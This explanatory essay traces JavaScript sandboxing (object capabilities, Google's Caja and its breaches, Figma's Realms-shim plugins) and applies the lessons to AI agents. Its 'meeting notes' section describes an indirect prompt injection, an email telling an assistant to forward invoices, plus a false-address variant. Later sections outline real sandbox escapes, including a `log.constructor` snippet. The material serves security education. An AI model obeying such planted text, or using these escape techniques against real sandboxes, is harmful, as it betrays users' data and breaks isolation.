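# What JavaScript sandboxing teaches about separating trusted and untrusted text in AI agents

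## Untrusted code in a web page, untrusted text in an agent

Sandboxing means running a program so that it can reach only a limited part of the system around it. A web browser downloads and runs programs written in JavaScript, the language of web pages, from sites the user may never have heard of, but keeps them away from the files on the user's computer. Scripts from different companies still share almost everything when they run in the same page. From about 2007, engineers tried to build a second, finer sandbox within the page, so that it could run a stranger's code and give it only a few chosen powers.

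AI agents have brought back a version of the same problem. An agent is a language model that repeatedly calls tools (software functions that, for example, search a mailbox or send a message) until it has done what the user asked. Along the way it reads emails, web pages and documents that other people wrote. The model receives this text and the user's request in one input, and anything in that input can change what the agent does next.

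### A weather widget in a webmail page

Suppose a company adds a weather widget, a small script that another firm wrote, to its webmail page. The page is the host, the application that runs code it does not trust, and the widget is the guest. The widget needs only a box to draw in and a way to fetch the forecast. But *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011), the internet standard on how browsers divide up trust, explains that when a page names an outside script, the browser by default runs it with all of the page's own privileges. The widget can therefore read the user's messages, send mail in the user's name and empty the inbox without exploiting a bug.

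Browsers separate pages by origin, which is roughly the combination of protocol, host name and port in a web address. A page from one origin generally can't reach into a page from another. But an imported script counts as part of the page that imports it, whichever server it came from, so this boundary doesn't protect the page from the widget. Barth warns that if the browser withholds a few privileges from one script, the script can usually get them anyway, because nothing isolates it from the rest of its origin. The webmail company could put the widget in an iframe, a nested page with its own origin, and for a plain forecast that may be enough. An iframe is a poor fit for a widget that has to work closely with the page, such as one that marks rainy days in the user's calendar.

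Webmail has the same problem. *Caja* (Miller, Samuel and colleagues, 2008), the draft specification for Google's first large attempt at a sandbox inside the page, points out that if a webmail service let messages carry scripts, just opening a message could delete the inbox. Web applications therefore stripped out the scripts, which was safe but also removed anything useful they did.

The widget's power over the inbox is an example of ambient authority, which is power that code has because of where it runs, not because anyone granted it. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) describes it as authority "exercised, but not selected" by its user, and compares it to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens automatically for anyone allowed through. The weather script can call the page's delete function without presenting a credential because the call comes from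 inside the page.

### Handing over references

The Caja engineers had in mind an alternative older than the web, the object capability. Programs in languages like JavaScript consist of objects, which bundle data and functions, and one object can use another only if it holds a reference to it. An object capability is an unforgeable reference that both identifies an object and gives the right to use it.

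Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) explains the difference with a word processor. When a user picks a document from a menu, the operating system normally gives the program the file's name. The program can make up another file's name and open that file too, since it runs with all the user's permissions. In a capability system, the operating system would open the chosen file itself and hand the open file to the program. The user would still pick from the same menu, but the program could damage only the chosen document.

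The standard illustration, which Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, set out in detail, gives human names to three objects. Alice holds a reference to Bob and a reference to Carol. She sends Bob a message that includes the reference to Carol, and from then on Bob can use Carol as well. If Alice had lacked either reference, she couldn't have made the introduction. Miller and Shapiro compress the rule into "only connectivity begets connectivity": every access comes from some earlier access. In the webmail page, Alice is the host's code, Bob is the widget and Carol is the box for the forecast. The introduction might look like this:

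`widget.start(forecastBox, getForecast);`

The widget can now draw in the box and ask for a forecast. It has no reference to the inbox and can't make one from a name or number.

Ordinary JavaScript doesn't work like this, because all scripts in a page share one global environment and can find the inbox through it. The Caja specification claimed that a subset of the language does work this way. It defines the subset so that objects start with no powerful references and get new ones only when another object passes them.

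That makes it practical to follow the principle of least authority, which is to give each part of a system only the power its task needs. Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission, which is what a program may do to the objects it can reach directly, from authority, which is everything it can cause to happen, including through other programs. Suppose the host gives the widget permission to call a single function that puts text in the forecast box. If that function treats the text as HTML, the widget can write a new script into the box, and the browser will run that script with the page's full privileges, which gives the widget authority over the whole mailbox.

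The gap between permission and authority can also help the host. In *From E to EcmaScript and back again*, Miller shows a few lines of JavaScript that wrap a file in an object offering only its read functions. Another wrapper forwards calls until its owner switches it off. A host could give the widget either kind of wrapper and keep the real object to itself.

These measures are meant to provide a stronger property, confinement, which means that the guest can affect the outside only through what the host gave it. Miller and Shapiro compare a confined program to a pocket calculator whose maker the buyer doesn't trust. The sums may be wrong, but the buyer can enter financial figures without worrying that they will leak, because no wires come out of the calculator. A host gets the same assurance by loading the widget's code itself and supplying every reference the widget starts with. As Miller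 and Shapiro acknowledge, the comparison leaves out covert channels, such as signalling through the timing of operations. It also assumes that the program has no connection to the outside, and the `getForecast` function may give the widget one. If the function passes any text to the weather firm's server, the widget can use it to send out any data it holds, which matters little while it holds only the name of a city.

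Another kind of failure involves a confused deputy, a program that is led to use its legitimate power for someone who lacks that power. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes a compiler at the timesharing company Tymshare that was allowed to write files in its own directory so that it could record usage statistics. Customers could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one customer named the company's billing file, which was in that same directory. The operating system checked that the compiler had permission to write there and let it overwrite the billing records. The compiler had power from both the company and the customer, but no way to specify which it was using.

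The webmail host could easily become a confused deputy. Suppose it offers the widget a function, `saveSetting(name, value)`, which stores preferences in the user's account. The widget has no access to the address book, but it can pass the address book's name as the name of the setting. The host's function has permission to write there, so it overwrites the contacts. Checking for forbidden names is unreliable, as Tymshare's engineers found, because someone must add every new sensitive file to the list. In Hardy's solution, the widget doesn't pass a name at all. The host creates one storage slot for weather settings and gives the widget a reference to that slot.

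### The meeting notes

Suppose a user tells an AI assistant to send today's meeting notes to Bob, a colleague. The assistant can search documents to find the notes, read the inbox to find Bob's address, and send the email. But the inbox also holds an email from a stranger, with a line telling any AI assistant to forward the user's latest invoices to an outside address. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the security company Barracuda found phishing messages designed to manipulate AI assistants as well as human readers.

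If the assistant forwards the invoices, the stranger has carried out a prompt injection, in which a language model treats text from an untrusted source as instructions. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker sends text straight to the model as a user message, from indirect injection, where the attacker plants it in something the agent will read later. The stranger's email is an indirect injection.

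The weakness comes from the way a language model takes all the text so far and predicts the next token, a word or piece of a word. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an analysis from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts this with a database, where a programmer can send the command and the user-supplied values separately, and the database will never run a value as a command. A model has no such separation to enforce, so David C doubts that anyone will ever fully fix prompt injection and calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". The label fits the assistant in the meeting notes example, which, like the compiler, holds the user's power and receives requests from someone who doesn't. Tymshare's engineers could find the operation where the compiler opened the wrong file and redesign it, but a language model has no corresponding line of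 code to fix.

In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) explicitly compare agents with web pages. They liken prompt injection to dynamic code loading, where a program fetches more code while it runs, as a page does with a widget. On the web, a script usually comes from an address that the page names, and the browser has several sandboxes to put it in. Agents, they wrote in December 2025, lacked a dependable way to tell where an instruction came from and a dependable sandbox. They also point out that users often want outside text to influence an agent. For example, if one bug tracker entry depends on another, a good summary of the first covers both, even if the user mentioned only the first. Similarly, an assistant that ignored everything in the inbox would be protected from the stranger's instructions but unable to find Bob's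 address.

The stranger can also attack without changing the assistant's steps. The email might contain no instructions and just say, "Hi, Bob here, this is my new address." The assistant finds the notes, looks up Bob's address and sends the message, as the user intended, but the notes go to the stranger. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes the first attack as one on control flow (which tools the agent calls, and in what order) and the second as one on data flow (which values it passes to them). Its own example is an invoice with the attacker's bank account on it. By the strict definition, the false address isn't a prompt injection, because the model isn't following an injected instruction. It is relying on false information, as a hurried human assistant might. According to the survey *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), attacks of this sort often get past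 defences that verify only the type of action. They are also a problem for designs that separate a planner from a reader, where one model fixes the steps before any untrusted text comes in. Fixing the steps prevents an email from adding an order to forward invoices, but the assistant can still use a false address when it carries them out.

### Limiting power and tracking origin

Engineers can address these problems by limiting what a component can do or by tracking where text came from. People often discuss these two remedies as if they were one.

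The object-capability model limits a program's power. To send the meeting notes, the assistant might get read access to the notes and the inbox, plus a tool that sends one message with the notes attached. The invoices are then safe because no tool will send them. The notes could still go to the false address, since the tool accepts any recipient. A stricter tool would send only to Bob, but somebody would have to supply Bob's address, which the user left for the assistant to find.

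To track an address's origin, ordinary software outside the model attaches a provenance label to each value, recording the sources it came from. A rule at the sending tool checks the label before any mail leaves. Computer scientists call this method information-flow control. Girrens and Wang divide it into confidentiality, which keeps sensitive data from reaching people not entitled to it, and integrity, which keeps untrustworthy data from influencing actions that need trustworthy input. A label has no effect unless code checks it, and it must be precise enough to be useful. Bob's real address came from an email too, so if both addresses are labeled only "inbox", the rule must block both or neither.

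References don't record where text came from. A host can give the weather widget only a box and a forecast function, and three functions later still have no way to tell that a piece of text came from the widget. Browser makers once tried taint tracking, which follows untrusted data through the browser, but Barth reports that it was difficult to implement at the time. The terminology is also confusing, because CaMeL, a well-known agent design, uses "capabilities" to mean labels that record a value's origin and permitted readers, which are not object capabilities.

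The two remedies can work together, with the origin of the text deciding which privileges the model keeps. David C relays a rule of thumb from an exchange between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. In the meeting notes example, the assistant would have only the stranger's privileges once it had opened the stranger's email. The notes would stay private, and Bob wouldn't get them.

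JavaScript engineers have tried both remedies in real products, and some of those products failed. But the untrusted code was always a program with a clear beginning and end, and the host could decide what to give it before running it. The stranger's email is a few sentences in the middle of the assistant's own input. How much of what the engineers learned still applies when the untrusted input is text?

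## Caja: how it worked and why Google abandoned it

In the late 2000s many large websites let outside developers write gadgets, small programs that ran inside the site's own pages. *object views* explains that browsers did not isolate a gadget from the page around it, so sites including Facebook and Yahoo's home page rewrote each gadget's script on their own servers before adding it to the page. Caja, Spanish for "box", was Google's rewriter. Ihab Awad, one of its designers, recalls in *Google Caja* that Mike Samuel already had a prototype for adding extensions to Google Calendar when Mark Miller joined the company. Miller had created E, an object-capability language, and the group set out to build the same kind of security into JavaScript.

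They had to do it in the browsers people already used, so Caja changed the guest's code before the browser saw it.

### Rewriting the weather widget

In the 2008 design, the host passes the guest's source code through a program called the cajoler. The cajoler rejects code that breaks any of a list of rules, and rewrites the rest to add runtime checks. Miller and colleagues started from the 1999 JavaScript standard and removed whatever would let a guest get around these checks.

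The most obvious thing to remove was `eval`, a function that runs a string of text as code. A guest could build a string after the cajoler had finished, and the browser would run it unchecked. Caja leaves out `eval` and the `Function` constructor, which has the same effect, and offers a restricted substitute.

The cajoler also rejects any name that ends in two underscores, partly because Firefox used one such name, `__proto__`, for a property that would have let a guest create more objects like one it held. Caja keeps its own records under names ending in three underscores, and the same rule keeps those names out of guest code.

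These first checks look only at the program's text. Miller and colleagues thought it impractical to work out much more about a JavaScript program before it runs. For example, a guest can write `forecastBox[name]`, where `name` holds a property name computed while the program runs, so nobody can tell from the text which property the guest will read. The cajoler therefore replaces each property access with a call to Caja's runtime library, which checks the actual name when the access happens.

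Suppose the weather widget consists of two lines:

```
var text = getForecast("Oslo");
forecastBox.setText(text);
```

Under the rules in the specification, the cajoler would turn them into roughly this:

```
___.loadModule(function (___, IMPORTS___) {
  var getForecast = ___.readPub(IMPORTS___, "getForecast");
  var forecastBox = ___.readPub(IMPORTS___, "forecastBox");
  var text = ___.asSimpleFunc(getForecast)("Oslo");
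  ___.callPub(forecastBox, "setText", [text]);
});
```

The runtime library is named `___`. The original widget used two variables it never defined, `getForecast` and `forecastBox`. The browser would normally look for these free variables in the shared global environment, but the cajoler turns them into look-ups in `IMPORTS___`, an object that the host fills. The finished function has no free variables, so the widget can reach only what comes in through the function's two parameters.

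If the widget's author uses `document`, the browser's name for the page, the cajoler turns that into a lookup in the imports too. The host put no `document` there, so the widget gets `undefined`, JavaScript's value for something missing. The widget can't tamper with the imports object directly, because its code can't use names ending in three underscores.

The host can call the finished function several times, and each call creates a separate instance of the guest. Miller and colleagues give the example of a weather module, which shouldn't be able to communicate with another module that has access to the user's bank account. If the host wants two modules to communicate, it gives both a reference to the same changeable object.

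That separation would fail if guests could alter JavaScript's built-in objects. All arrays, for example, inherit their functions from one shared object, which a guest can reach without naming a global variable. One guest could leave a message there for another. Caja therefore froze these objects, so that any attempt to change them caused an error. The team knowingly kept two built-in features that could still weaken the separation. `Date` reveals the current time, which helps a guest receive signals through timing. `Math.random` produces random numbers, but a poor implementation could let one guest infer how often another had called it.

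Much of Caja's complexity came from the keyword `this`. It normally refers to the object whose function is running, but that depends on how the function is called. If guest code took a function out of its object and called it separately, `this` could become the global object, which in a browser gives access to the whole page. Caja classified functions by how they used `this` and restricted how guest code could call each type. Miller and colleagues also defined a smaller language without the keyword, called Cajita, or "little box". They recommended Cajita for new programs and kept the larger language so that developers could port existing ones.

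Miller and colleagues compared Caja with an operating system to explain the host's role. A rewritten guest is like an ordinary program, which can calculate anything but can't operate the disk or the screen by itself. The objects that the host supplies are like device drivers, which the guest calls and which then act on the page. The host writes these objects in unrestricted JavaScript, and Caja doesn't check that code. Miller and colleagues warned that it must maintain "delicate invariants that it is easy to get wrong" and advised hosts to write very little of it.

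### Taming the DOM, HTML and CSS

The weather widget's `forecastBox` needs one of these drivers because putting the real box in the imports would also give the widget access to the inbox. The real box is part of the Document Object Model (DOM), the browser interface through which scripts read and change a page. Every element in the DOM has an `ownerDocument` property that leads to the document containing it, and from there a script can reach everything else. Maffeis, Mitchell and Taly showed in *Object Capabilities and Isolation of Untrusted Web Applications* that a guest could use this property to escape from ADsafe, a Yahoo sandbox for advertisements, after a library function gave the guest a real DOM object.

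Caja therefore tamed the DOM, wrapping the interface so that guest code could use it safely. O'Reilly's *A Secure Approach* describes guest code inside a `div`, an ordinary section of a web page. When that code calls a DOM function, it gets Caja's version, which can carry out the request or refuse it. The set of available functions replaces a separate list of permissions. As Jasvir Nagra, who worked on Caja at Google, said at a meeting recorded in OWASP's *DOM Sandboxing* (2011), "that api is the policy". Guest code could still use an object called `window` as usual, even though Caja had supplied it.

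Safe wrappers are hard to write. ADsafe had a function that created any page element for a guest except a `script` element. Maffeis and colleagues got around this restriction by passing an object where the function expected text. JavaScript converts an object to text by calling a function that the object can supply, and theirs returned "div" during ADsafe's check and "script" when the browser created the element. They suggested looking the value up once in a fixed table and using only the result. Douglas Crockford, who ran ADsafe, quickly fixed the flaw, but similar mistakes are possible in every function of a tamed DOM.

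A gadget also brings its own HTML and may generate more as it runs. HTML can contain scripts, and even a link can contain code if its address begins with `javascript:`. CSS, the language that controls a page's appearance, can also do harm. According to documentation at Pentaho, Caja's sanitizer removes `style` tags because some browsers could run code inside them and because a style can affect the entire page. The weather widget could use a style to hide the webmail company's warning about a suspicious message. The sanitizer also lets the host rewrite the ids and class names in a guest's HTML to keep them separate from its own.

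By this point Caja was building a page within a page, which the project's Open Hub description calls a virtual iframe. In *A lighter, more easily deployable version of Caja*, a discussion of how to strip the system down, one contributor named its main parts as a DOM wrapper and a component that constructs HTML. Even without its JavaScript protection, Caja would have needed its list of permitted HTML and CSS. The list recorded how to parse each construct and what it was for, and without it parts of one guest could leak into another.

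Google promised host pages that guest code could share objects with other guest code and inherit the page's styling, but couldn't steal cookies or send the user to a phishing page. In *Some Thoughts Regarding Caja*, West (2008) accepted that Caja was a practical necessity but disliked how its protections affected well-built pages. A developer can write a search form in plain HTML so that it works without JavaScript, then use a script to improve it. After Caja processed the form, the form no longer worked without JavaScript.

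### What the 2010 proof covered

Miller and colleagues claimed that separate guests are isolated from each other, but the 2008 specification contained no proof. In 2010 Maffeis and colleagues proved the isolation for a simplified core of Cajita.

They first defined isolation in terms of memory. The guests are isolated if none of them writes to a place in memory that a later guest reads, and none reads or writes a place that the host has forbidden. Their model runs the guests one after another, which avoids the complications of running them at the same time.

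The objects a guest can reach may change as it runs. Suppose the weather widget and a calendar gadget share a changeable list. If the widget puts a reference to its forecast box in the list, the calendar gadget can use the box too. A proof has to establish a limit on how far access can spread this way.

Call the code that runs *t* and the other guest *u*. *H* is the memory before *t* runs, and *K* is the memory afterwards. Then auth(*H*, *u*) is an upper limit on what *u* could read or write if it started from memory *H*, and act(*H*) is every possible read and write on the memory that exists in *H*. If *t* writes nothing that *u* could read, *u*'s authority must stay the same. If *t* does write something that *u* could read, the following must hold:

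`auth(K, u) ⊆ auth(H, u) ∪ auth(H, t) ∪ (act(K) \ act(H))`

Afterwards, *u* can do at most what it could already do, plus what *t* could do, plus anything involving memory that didn't exist before. The calendar gadget can gain the forecast box from the widget, but it can't gain the inbox, because the widget never had it. The two conditions formalize the idea that all access comes from earlier access.

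Maffeis and colleagues call a language that meets these conditions authority safe. They proved that a host can isolate guests in any such language by giving them initial powers that can't influence one another. They then proved that core Cajita meets a stricter standard, capability safety, which applies similar limits to each reference and implies authority safety.

The proof for Cajita assumes that the two functions that check every property read and write never return `eval`, the `Function` constructor or certain built-in functions that a guest could use to reach the global object. If Google's implementation returned any of these, the theorem wouldn't apply.

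Maffeis and colleagues studied a simplified version of Cajita and presented their results as being about its design. They didn't try to verify Google's version. No formal specification of Cajita existed, so they inferred its rules from the published code. They based their model on the 1999 JavaScript standard and left its successor, ECMAScript 5, for later. The model included JavaScript's built-in objects but not the DOM. It also left out the translation from Valija, a larger dialect that Caja converted into Cajita. Developers with existing gadgets would mostly have used Valija, since it was much closer to ordinary JavaScript.

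### Where the sandbox broke

A year before the proof, an attacker could have escaped through the DOM. Caja's taming library, Domita, used constructor functions to put a safe wrapper around each real element. Guests could see the constructors because they needed them to tell kinds of wrapper apart. According to Caja's advisory of July 2009, guests could also call them in unintended ways to create fake wrappers. Felix Lee of Yahoo turned this into a full breach on Internet Explorer 6 and 7. The team tried to fix the flaw, but Awad showed that Lee's attack still worked, and they had to fix it again.

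Caja later gained a second mode for browsers that supported ECMAScript 5. These browsers could freeze objects natively, a feature Miller had promoted on the standards committee, so they could do some of what Caja's inserted checks had done. By 2014 the team had deprecated the original cajoler, as maintainer Kevin Reid mentions in *Dropping JsonML support in the Closure Compiler* (Lenz, 2014).

The new mode's security depended on freezing the basic objects correctly. Caja's February 2013 advisory reports that the process had missed some of them, so a guest might have been able to trick trusted code into running the guest's code outside the sandbox. The advisory also describes a flaw in the web address filter that let a guest insert an address containing code if the host's own rules allowed it. Two years later, Mozilla (2015) disclosed that Firefox could make some locked objects extensible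 again. The fault was in the browser, since Caja had locked the objects correctly.

The breach involving escaped variable names came from a flaw in how Caja recognized names in the guest's code. In its newer mode, Caja searched the code for possible variable names and replaced dangerous ones, such as `window`, with its own objects. But JavaScript lets programmers write a letter in a variable name as a numeric code. Caja didn't recognize names written this way, so a guest could reach the real `window`, which breached the sandbox completely. Michał Bentkowski, who found the flaw, writes in an account published by Securitum that it let him run a script with the privileges of Google Docs.

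Google fixed the problem in about two weeks, but the 2015 language standard had added another way to write the numeric codes. Caja's parser should have rejected the new form but sometimes didn't because of a separate bug, so Google needed a second fix. Even then, SecurityWeek reports, Google had left an old version of Caja running in a demonstration on its developer site. In 2008, Miller and colleagues had accepted Unicode characters only inside quoted strings until they knew how to allow them elsewhere safely.

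A smaller flaw resembled the confused deputy at Tymshare. Caja had an optional wrapper for Google's programming interfaces, and Reid (2016), in *Caja security advisory 2016-05-31*, warned that one of the wrapper's functions didn't check its arguments properly. A guest could use that function to call functions on the host's page that the guest had no reference to. The guest couldn't pass them any arguments, so the damage depended on what the page's functions did.

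By November 2017, browsers had added the `import` expression and asynchronous functions, both of which gave programs new ways to run code from a string. Caja's newer mode didn't account for either, and Reid (2017), in *Caja Security Advisory 2017-11-14*, called the result "a complete breach of the Caja sandbox". Caja had excluded `eval` and `Function`, but browser makers had in effect added more functions of the same kind. Miller and colleagues had listed "uncontrolled language growth" among JavaScript's problems nine years earlier. Reid's remedy was to return to parsing and rewriting all guest code, so that Caja would accept only language features it recognized. As a result, developers lost useful line numbers in error messages.

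The June 2019 breach came from how Caja handled HTML elements it didn't permit. Caja renamed them to something harmless, so a guest's `title` became `caja-v-title`. Browsers treat anything inside certain elements, including `title`, as plain text, even if it looks like HTML, and Caja did the same when it filtered the guest's HTML. But once the element was renamed, the browser read the text inside it as HTML, which Caja hadn't filtered. In *Caja Security Advisory 2019-06-06*, Reid (2019) described "a complete breach of the Caja DOM sandbox" and told hosts to upgrade immediately. Hosts that ran guests without a DOM were unaffected.

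All of these flaws were in parts that Maffeis and colleagues had left out of their proof or in code they hadn't checked, so none of them contradicts it. But a host needed those parts to work too. The guest's code ran in the same page as the host's, so once a guest got a reference to the real `window`, nothing else kept it from the user's data.

### Adoption and retreat

Yahoo was the first large company to depend on Caja. Willison (2008) noted in October that Yahoo's new application platform would use it, and in December quoted Ben Laurie, another of Caja's designers, on the launch for My Yahoo and Yahoo Mail. Laurie wrote that Caja had suddenly gained 275 million users and was probably the most widely used capability language ever. That figure presumably reflects the audience of Yahoo's services rather than the number of people who ran a gadget.

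Google used Caja in orkut, its social network, and in Apps Script, a tool for writing small programs that extend products such as Google Docs. Awad also describes a demonstration in Google Wave, a service that combined messages with shared documents. A Wave document could contain an active program, which could contain more Wave content, and Caja restricted what the program could do. Google cancelled Wave two days after what Awad calls "our triumphal demo" and closed orkut in 2014.

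Apps Script is the clearest case of Google replacing Caja. When Bentkowski tested it, developers could choose between two sandboxes for their HTML. NATIVE used Caja, while IFRAME put the content in an iframe on a randomly generated subdomain, which gave it a different origin from the Google Docs page. Google's *Migrating to IFRAME Sandbox Mode* says the company has retired every mode except IFRAME and automatically moved older programs to it.

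Some of those programs needed changes. For instance, NATIVE had prevented HTML forms from being submitted in the usual way, and developers had come to rely on that. In an iframe, a form without a destination would load a blank page before the developer's script had finished. The new mode also didn't work in Internet Explorer 9, an older browser that Caja had supported.

Other potential users got similar advice. In *Can Caja still be used in production?* (Bombach, 2016), a developer at the German newspaper *Die Welt* asked whether Caja could sandbox widgets that students wrote for its front page. Reid answered that iframes, where a site could use them, were "a much, much lighter-weight solution than Caja". Caja would probably handle simple interactive pages, but it was too slow for a 3D game and didn't support the browser feature the game would need.

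Bombach wanted to avoid iframes because eight of them seemed to make the whole site sluggish, especially on phones. The widgets also changed size, so the page and the iframe had to exchange messages just to adjust the layout, and some widgets had to work with the page or with one another. Reid agreed that the resizing was an "awful mess" and that slow iframes would be a good reason to want something like Caja.

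By January 2019, Miller was directing a user who wanted to run untrusted code to a separate library, SES (*sanitized eval with Caja*, 2019). Caja contained an older version of SES that mostly supported ECMAScript 5 features. A year later, Power (2020) asked in *Caja performance recommendations* how to run some 20 third-party components on one page without making it too slow. The last message in the thread, as listed in *Google Caja Discuss*, begins with the point that "the broad conclusion is not caja".

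Google then announced that it would archive the project on 31 January 2021. After that date, it would add no features and accept no patches, even for security problems.

### Why Google stopped

The only reason Google documented for abandoning Caja is in the archive notice. Google wrote that it hadn't actively maintained Caja or kept it up to date with research on web security, and that "as a result" its own engineers and outside researchers had reported several vulnerabilities. The 2017 breach fits this account, because Caja hadn't kept up with changes in browsers. The 2009 breach doesn't fit, because the team was working on Caja at the time and had released the affected version only two weeks before the advisory. Google also didn't explain in the notice why it had stopped maintaining Caja.

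A developer of LavaMoat, a later tool that uses Caja's descendant to isolate software packages, has blamed the DOM for being too large and too changeable to control. That developer was an outsider, but people who worked on Caja had described the same difficulty. Nagra told the 2011 meeting that Caja could now give guests virtual copies of JavaScript's basic objects, then added, "But we can't keep virtualizing," and asked what browser makers could change to help. Reid told Bombach that he couldn't say exactly what Caja supported, because browsers had no numbered levels of features for it to target and each new feature was a separate piece of work.

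The DOM was only part of the problem. The escaped names and the new language features of 2017 would have been just as dangerous to a host that gave guest code no access to the DOM. Taming the DOM was probably the main reason Caja was slow and hard to maintain, but the JavaScript language alone was enough to allow complete breaches.

Wave and orkut, which had used Caja, closed, and Apps Script moved to iframes. These changes are well documented, but it is an inference that they left Google with fewer reasons to pay engineers to keep Caja working. Awad says that two projects that grew out of Caja were underfunded, but doesn't say the same about Caja itself. Google may have stopped investing in Caja because these products no longer used it, or Caja's cost and risk may have helped lead Google to move Apps Script to iframes.

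The browser's own isolation had also improved. Google says that Apps Script's IFRAME mode is based on the iframe sandbox in HTML5, which lets a host restrict what a nested page may do. Google's documentation therefore shows that browser isolation replaced Caja in one important product, but the migration page doesn't give a reason for the change, and the archive notice doesn't mention iframes. Reid's advice to Bombach makes it plausible that Google gave up on Caja as a whole because browser isolation had improved, but this is again an inference.

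Even so, iframes didn't do everything Caja did. Nagra objected in 2011 that a sandboxed iframe still started with too much authority, including ways to scan the user's local network. The host could communicate with it only by sending messages, which Nagra called tedious, and it was unclear how to arrange the iframes if one guest's program used libraries from two others. In its archive notice, Google recommended its Closure toolkit for cleaning up HTML and CSS, but named no replacement for running a guest's scripts inside the host's own page.

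## Figma, Salesforce and vm2: sharing the host's JavaScript engine

In 2019 Figma, whose design editor runs in the browser, set out to let other developers write plugins for it. A plugin might check whether text has enough contrast, or translate every label in a drawing. Such plugins have to read and change the user's document, so they need a much closer connection to the host than a weather box does. According to Figma's *How to build a plugin system on the web*, the company looked at many earlier ways of sandboxing outside code. Some rewrote the code, as Caja did, but most had never run in a production application. Figma began with an iframe instead.

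### Why the iframe was too slow

The prototype gave each plugin an iframe with a null origin, which matches no website, so the browser would refuse the plugin's requests to figma.com. The plugin and the editor could communicate only by sending messages. Each round trip took about 0.1 milliseconds, so a plugin that read 10,000 properties one at a time would wait one second. Figma therefore had the plugin request a copy of the document, work on the copy and send its changes back.

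But some documents were enormous. The editor needed 14 seconds to serialize a design file from Microsoft (turn it into plain data that fits in a message) and send it, and the plugin couldn't start until then. Most plugins do something quick, such as swapping two selected shapes, so users wouldn't have put up with the delay.

Messages also made plugins harder to write. JavaScript can't stop and wait for the answer to a message, so the plugin's author had to mark each such point with the keyword `await`. Many of the people Figma hoped would write plugins were designers with little training in programming. One `await` to fetch the document at the beginning and one to send it back at the end would have been manageable, but some edits needed more. Resizing a frame, for example, can move everything inside it, and the rules for that were in the editor. After such a change the plugin's copy was out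 of date, so the plugin had to send its work back and fetch the document again.

Figma abandoned the prototype after about a month of work and decided that plugins had to run on the page's main thread, alongside the editor, and work on the real document. A badly written plugin could then freeze the editor, but Figma accepted this because users start each plugin themselves and would know what caused the problem.

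### A second set of built-in objects

One way to do this was to put a second JavaScript interpreter inside the page. Figma compiled a small one, Duktape, to WebAssembly, a low-level code format that browsers run in a separate block of memory. The experiment worked, but plugins ran more slowly and the browser's debugging tools couldn't inspect them.

Figma then found the Realms shim, a library from Agoric, the company where Mark Miller, one of Caja's designers, was chief scientist. A shim imitates a proposed language feature that browsers don't have yet. This one ran the plugin in the browser's own JavaScript engine, the component that executes JavaScript, so plugins kept their full speed. In simplified form, it worked like this:

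```
with (allowedNames) {
  eval(pluginCode);
}
```

The `with` statement makes the engine look up every free variable in a given object first. Here that object was a Proxy, which called a function chosen by the host on every property lookup. The function returned `undefined` for any name not on a list of allowed names, so a plugin that tried to use `document` got `undefined`. Caja had done the same job by rewriting each free variable before the browser ran the code.

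Even when global names are hidden, a plugin can still reach JavaScript's built-in objects. For example, `({}).constructor` creates an empty object and gets the function that built it. From there the plugin can reach `Function`, which turns text into code and runs it in the global environment that `Function` belongs to. The shim therefore created a hidden iframe from the page's own origin, which it used only as a source of fresh built-in objects and not as a sandbox. A set of built-ins with its own global object is called a realm. Inside the plugin's realm, `({}).constructor` led to the fresh built-ins, where the shim had replaced `Function` with a restricted version.

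The arrangement was safe only as long as no object from Figma's realm got into the plugin's. Suppose the host wants to let plugins print messages while their authors test them, and passes in a function, `log`, that writes to the browser's console. The function looks harmless, but it inherits from Figma's built-in objects because Figma's code created it. The plugin can write:

`log.constructor("return window")();`

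The constructor of any function is `Function`, in this case the host's unrestricted one. Calling it creates a new function in Figma's global environment, and that function returns the real `window`. Figma meant to let the sandboxed code print a line of text, but in ordinary JavaScript code can use any function it is given to reach the whole page.

To pass `log` safely, the host has to run code inside the plugin's realm that creates a wrapper, and give the plugin only that wrapper. The same danger applied to every argument and return value in Figma's programming interface, and the company didn't want its developers to have to consider it whenever they added a function. It wrote a membrane of about 500 lines, a layer of wrappers that mediates every object passing between host and guest. The membrane copied numbers and strings across and gave the host only an opaque handle for anything else,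 as though the plugin were running in a separate interpreter. The rest of the interface depended only on this layer, so Figma could change the engine underneath.

A Figma plugin that needs its own window or network access can open a null-origin iframe and exchange messages with it. Figma didn't try to make the DOM safe to expose to plugins.

### September 2019

On 14 September 2019, a GitHub user called XmiliaH publicly posted a way to escape the Realms shim. Agoric fixed it the same day. Over the next eight days, XmiliaH and another contributor, Richard Gibson, privately reported more holes. Warner grouped them all into four bugs, each of which allowed a full breach (*Realms-shim Security Updates*, 2019).

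The public one involved `eval`. The shim needed the browser's real `eval` once, to start the guest's code, so the Proxy had a switch that made it return the real function for one lookup and the safe version after that. XmiliaH's guest code called itself until the engine ran out of room for more calls. With the right timing, the resulting error occurred after the shim had turned the switch on but before it could turn it off. The guest's next lookup of `eval` then returned the real function, which gave the guest access to `window`.

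Another of XmiliaH's attacks used the shim's own errors. When code looked like it contained an HTML comment, the shim refused to run it and threw an error that was an object from the host's realm. The guest could catch this error and follow its chain of prototypes (the objects it inherits from) to the host's built-ins, as with `log`. Agoric already had a function that replaced host errors with new ones made in the guest's realm, and began to use it in more places. But that function was also vulnerable, because it used JavaScript syntax that relies on the built-in array object. A guest could alter that object in its own realm so that the guest's code ran in the middle of the function.

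Figma's *An update on plugin security* (2019) describes the company's response. Figma stopped approving new plugins on the day of the first report. It had reviewed every plugin by hand, but only for how well the plugin worked for users, and had relied on the sandbox for security. On Monday 16 September it started work on a replacement for the shim, and on Tuesday it deployed the patch for the public bug. On Wednesday it also blocked updates to existing plugins, because an update instantly reaches everyone who has the editor open. It shipped the replacement on 25 September and let developers publish again. An audit of the published plugins found no sign that any had exploited the vulnerabilities.

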